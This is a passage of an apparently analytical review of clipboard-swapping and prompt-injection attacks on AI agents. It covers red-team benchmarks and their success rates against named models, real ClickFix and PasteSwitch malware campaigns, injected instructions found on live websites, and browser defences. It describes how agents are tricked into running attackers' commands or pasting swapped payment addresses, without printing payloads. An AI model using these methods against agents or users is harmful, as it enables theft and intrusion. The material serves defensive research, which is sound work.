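*AutoRedClaw*, from October 2026, is the nearest match by name. It describes a system in which one AI model writes attacks on agents like OpenClaw, a personal assistant that keeps instruction files and memories between sessions. The "Clipboard and Dataflow Confusion" category described earlier is one of the system's twelve attack strategies. The researchers assembled 330 cases and ran them on seven harnesses, each with up to four models, one apiece from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and DeepSeek.

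The attacker in these tests has to leave text in something the agent reads, such as a web page, an email or a file, because the attacker cannot send messages as the user. In 150 cases, the text is meant to get the agent to save a malicious rule or skill in its permanent files. Another 150 start with the malicious material already saved and test whether the agent acts on it. The last 30 are ordinary prompt injections, meant to misdirect the agent within a single session. Automated checks of files and application records then determine whether the attack worked.

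| Harness | Agent saved the malicious material | Agent acted on saved material |
|---|---|---|
| OpenClaw | 65.7% | 69.2% |
| Nanobot | 64.2% | 73.5% |
| NemoClaw | 56.2% | 50.9% |
| ZeroClaw | 26.3% | 35.8% |
| SeClaw | 13.0% | 10.5% |
| Codex | 65.0% | 65.0% |
| Claude Code | 26.7% | 21.7% |

Each of the first five rows is an average over three or four models. The two coding agents, Codex and Claude Code, each ran with one model on a smaller set of cases. SeClaw had low rates, but it completed only about half of the users' legitimate tasks, compared with roughly three quarters for OpenClaw.

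The ordinary prompt injections succeeded in 7 of 30 cases (23.3%) against Codex with GPT-5.4 and 5 of 30 (16.7%) against Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.5. This difference is too small to rank the two agents. Newer versions have since replaced both models.

All these rates are higher than they would be for freshly written attacks, because the researchers kept an attack only if it had already worked in a trial run, by default with DeepSeek V4 Pro on OpenClaw. Among the first 1,500 attacks they generated, 20.1% of those aimed at saving malicious material passed the trial, as did 46.1% of those that began with the material already in place. The benchmark therefore measures how well proven attacks transfer to other agents.

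A chart breaks the results down by strategy for five of the harnesses, but the text discusses only misleading interfaces and poisoned memory and gives no rate for the clipboard category. Such a rate would be hard to interpret because the category also covers uploads, autofill and file selection, and these agents often move data with file and shell tools that don't use the clipboard. More importantly, the attacks rely on instructions that the model reads and follows, whereas a Copy button can put different text on the clipboard without the page displaying any instructions.

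### Changes that a screenshot doesn't show

*Temporal UI State Inconsistency in Desktop GUI Agents*, from April 2026, tests attacks that the model has no chance to read. In its measurements on ten desktop tasks, Claude Opus 4.6 took an average of 6.51 seconds (range 3.18 to 13.23) to get from a screenshot to the resulting click. If the screen changes in that time, the agent clicks on something that wasn't in the screenshot.

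The most relevant of the study's three attacks modifies a web page. The agent sees an ordinary checkout form and decides to click "Place Order". One second after the screenshot, an invisible layer over the page becomes active, catches the click and sends the form to the attacker. The attack succeeded with Claude in all 15 trials on each of three tasks. It also succeeded in every trial with Qwen3.6-plus, an Alibaba model, and in 91.1% of trials with GPT-4o. Claude reported that it had clicked "Place Order", which was true as far as it could tell.

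The other two attacks use desktop windows. A fake warning that filled the screen received 30 of Claude's 45 clicks, while a small banner and an ordinary dialog box received none. A hidden window that popped up over the button received all 45.

The proposed defence takes another screenshot just before each click. It compares the area around the target and then the rest of the screen with the earlier image, checks for suspicious new windows, and cancels the click if anything important has changed. With Claude, it stopped all 180 attacks that used desktop windows. It added less than a tenth of a second per action and raised no false alarms in 30 ordinary checks. It failed against the modified page because the invisible layer didn't change any pixels. The study proposes adding a check on the page's underlying structure.

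A Copy button that stores the wrong string is just as invisible, so comparing screenshots before the click would not catch it. A structural check might miss it too, because the button's script can be in place when the page loads, with nothing changing between the screenshot and the click. The substituted text is on the screen once the agent has pasted it, but this defence compares the screen with an earlier screenshot, so it would not detect that the string in the terminal differs from the one on the web page. All three points are inferences from how the defence works.

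The study assumes an attacker with much more power than pastejacking requires, one who can already run code in the user's desktop session, for example through a malicious application or browser extension. Someone with that access could install a clipper and ignore web pages. The assumption matters less for the page modification, because an attacker who owns the page can make the same change with the page's own script. This last point is an inference.

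*Visual Confused Deputy* (2026) goes further and assumes that the attacker has compromised the agent's own software. That software swaps the images of two buttons in the screenshot, so a model trying to acknowledge an alert resets credentials instead. In both studies, the model reasons sensibly from a picture that no longer matches the computer. This also happens after pastejacking, but there the model usually sees the screen again before any harm is done.

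### False data without hostile instructions

An agent can also be misled while it sees everything and still does what its user asked. Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, separate this from the more familiar kind of prompt injection. Suppose a model receives instructions I, trusted data T, such as the name of an email's sender, and untrusted data U, such as the body of the email. An attacker adds some text A to the untrusted part. The two attacks then differ in how the model treats A:

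Instruction injection: model(I, T, U + A) ≈ model(I + A, T, U)

Data injection: model(I, T, U + A) ≈ model(I, T + A, U)

The model may respond as though the attacker's text were part of its instructions, or it may carry on with the user's task as though the text were a trusted fact.

One of their demonstrations, like pastejacking, ends with the attacker's command running on the user's machine. A developer asks a coding agent to apply the fix that a project's maintainer recommended in an online discussion. The attacker posts a comment there, formatted so that the model mistakes part of it for a separate comment by the maintainer. Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI all ran the attacker's command. By default they ask the user for approval first, but the reasoning they displayed also attributed the command to the maintainer, so the user saw a request to run the maintainer's fix.

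Choi and colleagues tested an agent based on GPT-5.2 on 96 tasks involving simulated services such as email and banking. The attacker knew the format of the agent's data and could write content that the agent would later retrieve. With no added defences, data attacks, which planted false information, succeeded in 49.1% of 108 attempts, compared with 0.2% of 935 attempts for instruction attacks, which planted commands.

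They then added defences one at a time:

| Added defence | Data attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| None | 49.1% |
| Scan incoming text for injected instructions | 50.0% |
| Check that each action fits the user's request | 45.4% |
| Plan the steps before reading outside data | 40.7% |
| Put random labels on data fields | 28.7% |
| Keep untrusted data away from the main model | 25.0% |
| Restrict the agent's actions by policy | 22.2% |
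| Track strictly where each piece of data came from | 0% |

The scanner flagged 326 of the 935 instruction attacks but none of the data attacks. The action checker flagged 14 of the 108 data attacks and identified the real problem in only one. There was little for it to flag, because the agent was doing the task its user had given it. Strict tracking stopped every attack, but the share of ordinary tasks the agent could complete fell from 86.5% to 36.5%.

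Pastejacking would similarly leave an agent carrying out the right task with the wrong string, but the 49.1% figure doesn't estimate how often that would happen. A data attack has to make the model misread text in front of it, and these agents received their data as structured text, not screenshots. When a Copy button puts different text on the clipboard, the model reads the page correctly but can't see the error in the clipboard. That could make the attack easier, since the model doesn't have to misread anything, or harder, since the pasted string usually appears on screen afterwards.

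The comparison does help interpret the prompt-injection rates in system cards, the reports developers publish with new models. Those rates measure how often a model follows hostile text. GPT-5.2 almost never did, yet about half of the data attacks against it succeeded. OpenAI has since replaced that model, but a low injection rate for its successors would not on its own show that they can handle a swapped command.

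### From a web page to the terminal

Pastejacking commonly happens when a user follows a web page's instructions for installing something. *RedTeamCUA* (Liao, Jones and colleagues, 2025) tested agents on similar tasks. Agents on a Linux desktop had to find directions on a forum, in a chat or in a shared file, then install software, change a setting or set up a project. The researchers combined nine tasks with 24 attacker goals, such as deleting system files or leaking documents, and wrote four versions of each pair, for 864 cases.

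The attacker could post text only where any user of the site could. A typical post mixed genuine installation steps with a harmful one and gave a reason why the harmful step was necessary. In the main test, which began with the agent already on the page, the attacks succeeded in 66.2% of cases against GPT-4o and 42.9% against Claude 3.7 Sonnet. OpenAI's Operator had the lowest rate, 7.6%, largely because it stopped to ask the user for approval. When the researchers simulated an inattentive user who approved everything, the attack success rate against Operator rose to 30.9%.

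These figures count an attack as successful if it worked in any of three attempts, so the average chance of success on a single attempt may be lower. For Claude's 42.9%, that chance is between 17% and 43%. It is 17% if all cases were equally likely to succeed (1 − 0.83³ ≈ 0.43), and 43% if each case either always worked or never did.

Liao and colleagues then took 50 of the most successful cases and made the agents find the page themselves:

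| Agent | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
| Operator | 10% |
| Operator, user approves everything | 42% |
| Claude Opus 4 | 48% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 50% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 50% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 60% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 83% |

Older models often failed to find the page or to finish the harmful task. Claude Opus 4.5 was more competent, so it completed more of the attacker's work. Claude Opus 4.6 recognised the attack in 25 of the 50 cases and was fooled in the other 25. Later models have since replaced every agent in the table. The rates are also near the worst case, because the researchers chose attacks that had succeeded.

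*RedTeamCUA* tests the same path from web page to terminal that pastejacking uses, but its attacker can post text but can't run a script on the page, and so has to persuade the agent. A pastejacker controls the page's script and doesn't need to persuade it. Claude Opus 4.6 protected itself by noticing hostile text, which a page that swaps the copied command needn't contain. The success rates also don't distinguish commands that an agent typed from commands it pasted. The study does establish that agents will take a command from the web and run it locally as part of a routine job.

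Researchers have continued to test this kind of task. In *AgentHijack* (2026), a user asks an agent to open a terminal and prepare to install tmux, a terminal utility. The attacker controls one image on a technical web page and has optimised it to alter the agent's next action. *Conartist* (2026) reuses the *RedTeamCUA* cases to study prompt injections that unfold over several steps. Both studies interfere with what the model sees or reads, so neither tests what happens when the page is accurate but the clipboard's contents are not.

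### Running code without reading it

A swap's success depends a good deal on whether the agent looks at the command before running it. The best evidence comes from 13 code-injection tasks in Ding and colleagues' April 2026 study of benign instructions. In these tasks, the user makes a reasonable request, such as setting up a software project, and the attacker controls the project's files. Claude Sonnet 4.5 caused harm in 10 of the 13 tasks and Claude Opus 4.5 in 9, counting a task if any of three attempts caused harm.

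Neither model ever opened a setup script before running it. Both read the project's introductory file and followed its instruction to run the script. Claude Opus 4.5 did open a script that arrived on its own as an email attachment, and it found the malicious code. A tidy, well-documented project apparently made it less likely to check. This suggests that an agent might trust the fake Homebrew pages described earlier for the same reason, since they look just as professional.

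A pasted command is easier to inspect than a script because it appears in the terminal without the agent opening a file. An agent that never opens scripts might still notice that a command has changed. But if the command only downloads a script and runs it, as many install commands do, the dangerous code is in a file the agent hasn't read.

Some agents use one model to plan the task and another to operate the screen, which could make the comparison harder. Ding and colleagues retested 43 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had refused when working alone. The model caused harm in 27.9% of them when given the user's original request, and in 79.1% when given a planner's list of subtasks instead. By inference, a swapped command could pose a similar problem, because a model told only to paste what was copied and run it may never have seen the web page and would then have nothing to compare the command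 with.

A general warning to check for harmful actions and refuse them helped somewhat. It halved Claude Opus 4.5's failures on 50 tasks that the model had previously failed every time, but reduced Claude Sonnet 4.5's failure rate only from 98% to 84%. The warning did not include the much more specific instruction to compare what the models had copied with what they had pasted. Anthropic has replaced both models.

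### The missing experiment

The simple test outlined earlier compares honest and dishonest Copy buttons. A fuller version would vary three other things as well:

| What changes | First version | Second version |
|---|---|---|
| Copy button | Stores the displayed string | Stores a different one |
| String | Install command | Payment address |
| Committing action | In a separate response, after a new screenshot | In the same batch as the paste |
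| Access to the clipboard | The agent can read its contents | The agent can't |

That makes 16 combinations. For a payment, the committing action is clicking Send, not pressing Enter. The page should contain no instructions aimed at the agent, or the experiment would measure prompt injection, as Rehberger's test did.

A replacement command that appears to download an installer from the wrong address is better than an obviously harmless one, which an agent might notice and sensibly run anyway. The test should run inside a sealed network where that address serves a script that only leaves a marker file. The command should not end in a line break, so that the agent can inspect it before it runs. Payments can use a test network whose coins are worthless. Some false payment addresses should match the real one at both ends and others should differ throughout, to show whether the agent compares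 whole strings.

The experiment needs two rounds because an agent may do the task without using the clipboard. In the first round, the agent chooses its own method, which shows how often it uses the clipboard. In the second, the user tells it to use the Copy button, which shows how often it notices a swap after pasting. Liao and colleagues placed agents directly on the page with the attack for a similar reason, since researchers can't measure how well an agent resists an attack it never reaches.

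A model that is free to batch actions may choose not to, so it is also worth measuring how often it batches them. To test how batching affects the outcome, researchers could compare a single tool that pastes and presses Enter with a harness that allows one action per turn and always returns a screenshot.

The harness's list of actions won't be enough to reconstruct what happened. In the hidden-form case from *A Systematization of Security Vulnerabilities in Computer Use Agents*, the agent's click looked like any user's in later logs. A click on a Copy button that substitutes different text would presumably leave the same record as a click on one that copies the text shown. The researcher should save the clipboard's contents after every action, along with each screenshot the model receives, and use the marker file or the test payment to decide whether the attack succeeded.

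Running each combination in the second round 50 times would take 800 runs, half of them with a swapped string. Of those 400, 200 would use batched actions and 200 separate ones, enough to estimate the difference to within about 10 percentage points. If the agent ignored the request and retyped the string in half of the runs, the margin would widen to about 14 points. The commands, addresses and page designs should vary, because repeated runs on one page resemble each other. Each run should be counted separately, because counting the worst of three attempts would exaggerate how often an ordinary user is at risk.

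Testing buttons that copy the displayed text matters as much as testing buttons that swap it, because an agent that refused to paste anything would avoid every swap but be useless. Ding and colleagues saw a milder form of this excessive refusal with MirrorGuard, a safety monitor for computer-use agents. It greatly reduced harm with one open-source model, but the protected agent also refused 17 of 36 ordinary tasks.

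Experiments should report a separate rate for each of the four conditions for harm, because the conditions call for different remedies. If agents catch nearly every swap when they get a screenshot before pressing Enter, but miss nearly every one when the actions are batched, developers could fix most of the problem by splitting the batch. If agents miss swaps even with both strings in view, another screenshot won't help, and the harness would have to compare the strings itself.

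## Records of clipboard attacks on people

Criminals already run web pages that attack people through the clipboard, and an agent browsing the open web can land on the same pages. Security firms' records show the kinds of attacks an agent might encounter there, though most of the recorded victims are people.

### How common ClickFix is

The most quoted figure, that ClickFix accounts for 47% of attacks, comes from the *Microsoft Digital Defense Report* (Microsoft, 2025). Microsoft's Defender Experts, who watch customers' systems for intrusions, found that ClickFix was the way in for 47% of the attacks in their notifications. Phishing came second at 35%, and software vulnerabilities accounted for only 1%. Microsoft does not give the number of attacks behind these percentages. The Hacker News' *Threat Actors Don’t Want Better Attacks. They Want Repeatable Ones* (2026) repeats the 47% figure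 as a statistic for "last year".

The 47% figure covers July 2024 to June 2025, according to Microsoft's *Extortion and ransomware drive over half of cyberattacks* (2025), so it was over a year old when the trade press repeated it. The Hacker News' *17,000 URLs Reveal How ClickFix Turns Trusted Websites Into Malware Traps* (2026) assigns it to calendar year 2025, which is slightly wrong. Microsoft dates the surge in ClickFix to November 2024, four months into the period. If ClickFix was rarer before then, its share in the remaining eight months must have been above 47%.

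The same report gives quite different figures from Microsoft's incident response team, which investigates breaches. The team attributed 10% of its cases to social engineering, 6% to phishing, which it counted separately, and 11% each to flaws in public-facing applications and the use of valid accounts. In another 20%, it identified no way in. ClickFix has no category of its own in these figures and would most naturally fall under social engineering. The two sets of figures may differ because the notifications include many attacks that defenders stopped early, while the response team sees the ones that became serious (an inference).

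More recent figures also measure different things. Beazley Security's *Quarterly Threat Report* (2026) attributes 19% of ransomware cases in the third quarter of 2026 to malware, "mostly ClickFix", so ClickFix's share was between about 10% and 19%. Johnson (2026), in *IR trends Q3 2026*, found that phishing was still the most common way attackers got in among cases handled by Cisco's security group Talos. In June, Palmer (2026) reported in *ClickFix Now Cybercriminals' Favorite Malware Delivery Technique* that ReliaQuest, another security firm, had concluded that ClickFix had become the most common way to deliver malware.

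| Source | Period | What it counts | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft's Defender Experts | July 2024–June 2025 | Attacks in notifications to customers | ClickFix: 47% |
| Microsoft's incident response team | July 2024–June 2025 | Breaches it investigated | Social engineering: 10%; phishing, counted separately: 6% |
| Beazley Security | July–September 2026 | Ransomware cases | Malware, mostly ClickFix: 19% |
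| Johnson | July–September 2026 | Talos incident-response cases | Phishing in first place |

These results can all be correct. Many intrusions start with a stolen password and need no malware, so ClickFix could be the most common way to deliver malware without being the most common way to start an intrusion. The categories also overlap, because a phishing email can send its reader to a ClickFix page. Microsoft's suggested reading on ClickFix includes a phishing campaign that impersonated Booking.com. Results for other attacks also depend on the dataset. Verizon, as quoted by The Hacker News, found that attackers got in through vulnerabilities in 31% of its cases, while Microsoft's figure was 1%.

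The evidence therefore supports the claim that ClickFix is one of the main ways attackers get into organisations, but not that it causes half of all attacks. The takeaways Microsoft (2026) published from its next report, which covers July 2025 to June 2026, still list ClickFix-style tricks among the heavily exploited ways in, but give no percentage. Apple and Opera have changed their software in response to clipboard attacks.

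The Hacker News reports that CTM360, a security company, linked 17,000 web addresses to ClickFix. The figure counts pages rather than victims, and one group can put up many pages. Some of the addresses were on trusted sites, which suggests that an agent can't avoid these pages just by staying on reputable websites.

### Advertisements from HBO Max's Reddit account

In September 2026, attackers used HBO Max's verified Reddit account to publish 108 malicious advertisements in 48 hours. A Reddit user, Alex Cutts, noticed one promoting a nonexistent HBO Max app for Mac. The advertisement led to a convincing copy of an HBO Max page, where the download button brought up instructions to copy a command and paste it into a terminal.

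Hudson Rock's *HBO Max ads on a compromised Reddit account* (2026), based on joint research with ADAMnetworks, sorts the 108 advertisements by destination: 46 led to fake HBO Max sites, 47 to sites posing as AI or developer tools, and 15 to a supposed disk cleaner for Macs. The developer tools matter most for agents. Few people would ask an agent to install a streaming app, but many might ask it to set up a coding tool, and an agent that clicked one of these advertisements would reach a page listing the steps it expected to perform (an inference).

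Hudson Rock traced the advertisements to a larger operation that it calls PasteSwitch. The operation's servers check each visitor to select what to deliver. On Macs, the malware included fake versions of cryptocurrency wallets such as Ledger and Exodus, and programs that steal passwords. Microsoft had separately reported that one of these programs, MacSync, arrives through commands that victims paste into Terminal. Windows visitors got loaders, small programs that fetch other malware.

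PasteSwitch also distributed clippers. We infer that if a person pastes the command and installs a clipper, an agent that later uses the same desktop could copy a correct address from a legitimate website but paste the attacker's address instead.

The page told visitors to copy the command themselves, so it may not have written anything to the clipboard. In that case, the attack resembles the cloned installation pages described earlier, where the malicious command is visible on the page.

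### A browser script that replaces payment addresses

*ClickFix moves into the browser* (Gallagher, 2026) describes a campaign that Talos has tracked against users of two cryptocurrency trading sites since it began in October 2025. The attackers posted what looked like a leaked report of a nonexistent flaw that would supposedly let traders collect bigger payouts. They told readers to exploit it by pasting code into Chrome's address bar, much as scammers had persuaded Facebook users to do around 2011. A later version had readers paste the code into Tampermonkey, a legitimate browser extension for running custom scripts, which reloads the code whenever they return to the trading site.

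The code then changes the trading site inside the victim's browser. When the site's server sends a deposit address, the code replaces it with the attackers' address before the page displays it. It also replaces addresses on the clipboard and adds fake "bonus" messages to the page so the trick seems to be working. The attackers had kept their scripts in a Google Sheets document since March 2026. In July, after text-sharing sites kept disrupting their posts, they moved the whole campaign to Google's services.

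This theft happens entirely inside a browser, on an otherwise genuine website. Most ClickFix victims instead paste a command into the operating system, where security software may detect it.

An agent working in a browser where the user had already installed this campaign's script could not detect the swap by comparing the pasted address with the one on the page, because the script changes both. It would need to compare the pasted address with one from elsewhere, such as the user's original request or a second device. Both points are inferences from how the script works.

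None of the figures above measures how much money clippers steal. Payments on most cryptocurrency networks are public, so investigators who know an attacker's address can add up what it has received. But that total would miss payments to addresses that nobody had connected to the malware, and it could include money from other scams that used the known addresses.

### Why these counts give no rate for agents

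Incident records include only attacks that somebody detected. They leave out visitors who saw the page and closed it, so they don't give a success rate even for people. In a hypothetical case, 10,000 people open a ClickFix page, 50 paste the command, and security software detects 30 of those attacks. The true success rate is 0.5%, but nobody could calculate it from a record of 30 attacks.

An agent might refuse the page's instructions more often than human visitors do, or it might follow them more often because it is trying to complete its task and isn't deterred by an annoying or strange verification prompt. Rehberger's test showed that Claude 3.7 Sonnet could fall for such a page, but neither his test nor these records show how often agents do.

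The records also mostly describe planted text that comes with instructions. Swapped text is harder to find in them, perhaps because it is rarer, but also because victims have less to report. Someone who pasted a command into the Windows Run dialog to prove they were human may later realise that this was odd, but someone who used the fake Homebrew button got Homebrew, as they expected, and might never connect a stolen password with that installation. This suggests that the counts may most understate swapped text, the attack that needs the least cooperation from an agent.

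### Terminal commands addressed to agents

Some websites now carry text written for AI agents. Sewani's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild* presents ten examples that researchers at the security firm Forcepoint found by searching live sites for stock phrases used to override a model's instructions. Hackread's *Hackers Use Hidden Website Instructions in New Attacks on AI Assistants* dates the finds to April 2026.

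Only one of the ten texts contains a terminal command. The command would delete a directory whose name suggests it may hold backups, and Sewani thinks it targets coding assistants and other agents with shell access. This text is visible on the page, while most of the others are hidden from human readers. Two others are meant to obtain money. One gives step-by-step directions for sending $5,000 through PayPal, and the other directs agents to a donation link.

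Judging by their content, several of the rest look more like pranks or self-promotion than crime. One is a request for a poem about corn, and another is an instruction for AI systems to credit the site's author and repeat the word "cows".

These texts are prompt injections, not clipboard attacks, because the agent has to read the command and decide to run it. Sewani's examples show only that the text was on the pages. He documents no agent that obeyed any of it, though he describes the technique as "actively weaponized". His search can also match articles that warn about these attacks, as he acknowledges, because they contain the same phrases, and it would presumably miss a page that used different wording.

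Other researchers have found similar pages. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* reports that Google published a study in the same week as Forcepoint, drawing on a collection of 2 to 3 billion crawled pages a month. Unit 42's *Fooling AI Agents* also reports prompt injection on live websites. According to a summary in VPN Central's *Indirect prompt injection attacks are no longer theoretical*, the attackers' aims included destroying data and making unauthorised payments, and one page contained 24 separate attempts.

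The two campaigns in Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* look more like organised fraud than most of Forcepoint's examples. One site posed as software documentation to run a payment scam, and the other impersonated a cryptocurrency service. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, the attackers pushed both sites up the search results, which made agents more likely to find them, and hid the instructions from human visitors. Someone who already builds fake documentation for agents could, with very little extra work, add a Copy button that puts the wrong command on the clipboard. This is an inference, and neither campaign is known to have done it.

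### The closest recorded incident

These records include no confirmed case of a clipboard attack harming an agent. The closest is an incident that Field Effect, a security company, detected on a Mac on 23 April 2026. A session of the agent Claude Code in the code editor Cursor downloaded and ran AMOS, a program that steals passwords, access keys and cryptocurrency wallets. The malware uploaded the first stolen data less than two minutes after the first download. It also asked the user for their Mac password in a fake system dialog and installed a second program that would keep running after the theft.

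Field Effect concluded that someone had tricked the person operating the agent. The download came from a domain that earlier reports had linked to a ClickFix-style campaign that used fake troubleshooting guides for Claude Code. The operator may have copied text from such a guide and pasted it into the agent's prompt. That would make the incident a scam on a person in which the agent carried out the last step, but this is a guess, and Field Effect doesn't mention the clipboard. The agent ran its commands directly rather than operating a desktop through screenshots and clicks. Hudson Rock later noted that part of the PasteSwitch malware stays on a Mac in a similar way.

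Attackers have also delivered AMOS through agents, without a web page to copy from. Trend Micro found hundreds of malicious skills (add-on instructions for agents such as OpenClaw) in public collections. The attackers again used a dialog box to trick the user into entering a password.

Microsoft (2026) reports a May 2026 analysis in which AI browsers were the first point of infection in incidents involving 57 malware families. The figure doesn't show whether the clipboard or the agent played a part, because users may have downloaded the malware themselves.

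A real clipboard attack on an agent could also go unrecognised. Field Effect found the malicious commands hard to distinguish from ordinary work, because coding agents download and run scripts all the time. A swapped command that an agent pasted would look much the same to monitoring software, unless the software also recorded the clipboard's contents and the page that put them there (an inference). Microsoft advises companies to watch for unusual clipboard activity followed by a shell launching. That might catch such an attack, but an agent that copied and pasted a genuine install command could set off the same alert.

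## Browser limits on writing to the clipboard, and labels for where text came from

Browsers limit when a web page can write to the clipboard, and one, Opera, also checks what the page writes. Both defences act before anyone pastes, so in principle they could protect an agent that never checks its work. Some browsers also label copied text with the address of the page it came from, which the receiving program could use to decide whether to accept the text.

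### When a page may write

User activation is a browser's record that the visitor has clicked or pressed a key. Browsers require it before a page can do certain things, such as open a pop-up window. WHATWG's *User interaction*, a chapter of the HTML standard, distinguishes two kinds. Sticky activation starts with the visitor's first click or keypress on the page and never ends. Transient activation lasts at most a few seconds after each click or keypress, so that the visitor has a chance to connect what they did with what the page did next.

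Clipboard writes depend on transient activation, which lasts five seconds in Chrome, according to text/plain's *Browser basics user gestures* (2020). Lawrence says there that he last verified the figure in June 2025. WebKit's *The User Activation API* notes that each browser engine sets its own limit and deliberately hides it from the page.

The draft standard from W3C sets out the check a browser runs when a script asks to write:

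1. If the user has given the site permission to write without a click, the browser allows it.
2. If there was a recent click or keypress, the browser allows the write when the user pressed a copy control belonging to the browser or operating system. Otherwise it requests the ordinary write permission.
3. If there was no recent click or keypress, the browser requests the stronger permission from step 1.

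Remote-desktop sites need the stronger permission because they sync two machines' clipboards even when the user isn't clicking. Browser makers choose the default for each permission, so a browser can grant the ordinary permission without showing a prompt.

*Web-Facing Change PSA* (Stade, 2024) reports that Chromium, the open-source code behind Chrome, accepts plain-text writes to the clipboard after any user gesture, and that other browsers don't use clipboard permissions at all. Stade (2024) explained later that month that richer formats need more than a generic click in Chromium, but commands and payment addresses are plain text, so the stricter rule doesn't cover them. WebKit, Safari's engine, has a test to confirm that a script can't write text without a gesture.

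Chrome used to be less strict than Safari and Firefox. W3C's *Interoperability issue* records a 2022 complaint that Chrome let pages write to the clipboard without a user gesture, which the other two browsers did not allow. Stade (2022) replied that Chromium now required either user activation or an explicit grant of permission, but Goulikar (2024) remarked in passing that Chromium still lacked the activation requirement. Stade's account is probably more reliable because he was describing a specific code change. The disagreement makes no difference once an agent has clicked on the page.

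The page must also have focus, meaning roughly that it is receiving keyboard input. A malicious page in a background tab therefore can't use this interface to replace an address that an agent copied from another site. A page also loses access when the agent switches to a terminal. The focus rule works without anyone having to notice an attack, so we can infer that it should protect agents as well as it protects people.

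The draft's check tests for activation but doesn't use it up, so a page that has focus could write to the clipboard several times after one click, before the activation expires. A button could copy the displayed command and replace it a second later (also an inference). A click inside an embedded frame, such as a video player, activates the page around it too.

Copy events are exempt from the permission. A script can't change the clipboard by faking a copy event, but when a user presses the copy shortcut, the page can supply its own text. W3C allows browser makers to let users turn this feature off or limit it to chosen sites. None of these rules requires the browser to compare the text a page writes with the text it displays.

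### Whether an agent's click counts

Lawrence ranks user gestures among the weakest protections against abusive pages, because a site can easily trick visitors into clicking. Requiring a gesture treats a click as a sign of what a person wants, but when an agent uses the browser, software produces the click.

Browsers reject some clicks made by software. Only events that the browser marks as trusted count as user activation, and a click generated by the page's own script is untrusted, so a malicious page can't gain user activation by clicking its own buttons. The mark doesn't test whether a human clicked. Google Chrome's *Event.isTrusted Sample* says it is mainly for browser extensions that need to know whether a script sent an event.

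A desktop agent's clicks reach the browser as ordinary mouse input, so they presumably do count, as the demonstrations against Claude and Atlas suggest.

Automation tools can also produce user activation. In Mozilla's copy of the test suite that browser makers share, the clipboard tests get their activation from a click that an automation driver performs. Firefox 121 added a way for a tool to run a script as though the user had just acted, which jgraham requested in *Add support for "userActivation" parameter to script evaluation*. In Chromium, the tests for a built-in agent's click tool include code that watches for a user gesture.

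If a harness instead presses buttons by running a script inside the page, the browser should treat the click as untrusted and block the clipboard write. Copy buttons would then fail whether or not they copy the text shown on the page (this is an inference).

It is debatable whether browsers are wrong to accept an agent's click. W3C's *Web User Agents* (2026) counts AI systems that act on a person's behalf as user agents, like browsers. On that view, the click expresses the user's wishes because the user delegated the task. But someone who asks an agent to install a program has hardly agreed to every clipboard write on every page the agent visits.

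Asking for permission may not help much. W3C's *Agentic Browsing and the Web's Security Model* (2025) includes minutes from a November 2025 standards session, where one participant pointed out that an agent can click "yes" when a site asks for confirmation. An agent could do the same with a browser's prompt. In Chromium, an explicit grant covers many later writes. By inference, an agent that accepted one could let the site write to the clipboard without a click whenever the page had focus, even after the user had taken over the browser.

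Another participant proposed treating the agent as separate from the browser, so that the browser could enforce rules on it. A browser with a built-in agent can identify that agent's clicks and could deny them clipboard access. Denying them user activation altogether would be impractical, because file uploads and pop-up windows also depend on it. The browser couldn't apply either rule to a desktop agent whose input looks like a person's.

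Browsers enforce the activation rule automatically, but an agent satisfies it by clicking or typing on the page. The rule still protects an agent that only reads the page's text.

### What Opera's Paste Protect blocks

Opera's Paste Protect has two parts, both on by default. Hijack protection dates from 2021, and Opera added Injection protection on 2 July 2026.

Opera's injection protection is designed to stop ClickFix attacks. It checks anything a user or website copies in the browser for patterns common in malicious commands, using different patterns for Windows, macOS and Linux (Opera, 2026). These patterns include PowerShell commands and encoded fragments, according to Antipov's *Ctrl+C, Ctrl+V, Ctrl+стоп. Opera вмешалась в святое* (2026). If the text matches, Opera blocks the copy before it reaches the clipboard, opens a pop-up and shows a red icon in the address bar. The user can view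 up to the first 120 characters of the blocked text, hold a button for more than five seconds to copy it anyway, or always allow copying from that site.

The block takes effect without anyone's attention, so it should also protect an agent that uses Opera. It might have stopped the planted command in Rehberger's test, but not in the variation where Claude typed the command, because nothing passed through the clipboard there. After a block, the clipboard presumably keeps its earlier contents, so an agent that missed the pop-up would paste old text. An agent could also override the block if its harness can hold down a mouse button, though allowing the site would be easier. These are inferences from Opera's description.

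Swapped install commands are harder to catch because they may differ from the genuine ones only in the web address. A filter that checks only the form of a command would block both or neither. Opera expects some false alarms and suggests that developers who often copy commands from trusted sites such as GitHub add those sites to the allowed list. Swapped commands from those sites would then get through too. Opera gives no figures for how many attacks the feature catches or how many genuine commands it blocks.

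Hijack protection covers sensitive data such as an IBAN, the international form of a bank account number. Opera says it has copied the number securely and warns the user if something tries to replace it. The original release notes, quoted in Softpedia's *New feature now available in the latest dev build*, also mention cryptocurrency wallets and describe a defence against clippers: Opera monitors the copied data for a while, or until the user pastes it, and warns if an "external application" changes it.

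A page that swaps the address during copying would probably get past Opera's Hijack protection. The attacker's address would reach the clipboard first, and Opera would guard it against later changes. The browser might even report that it had copied the attacker's account number securely. Opera's announcement and Antipov's summary both mention websites that replace copied text, but Opera's explanation of how Hijack protection works refers only to external applications. Injection protection wouldn't help either, since an address doesn't look like a command.

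Even against a clipper, Hijack protection depends on someone noticing the warning. An agent that had already switched to a wallet program might never see it.

### What a terminal could do with a source label

Provenance is a record of which site or application a piece of data came from. Windows has recorded this for downloaded files since 2003, so that it can scrutinize files from the internet more closely after they reach the disk. The clipboard has no exact equivalent, but Lawrence's "text/plain" describes several similar features. In 2011, Internet Explorer began storing the source address on the clipboard alongside the copied text. Chromium and Firefox now have their own versions. Most programs can ignore the label, because the clipboard holds it as a separate format.

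Lawrence understands that Chromium's label was originally for data-loss prevention, or stopping confidential material from leaving a company. He proposes also using it for security. A program that receives a paste could look for the label, check which Windows security zone the address belongs to, and prompt the user if necessary. He worries that these prompts would annoy users, since he roughly estimates that pasted text is harmless 99.99% of the time.

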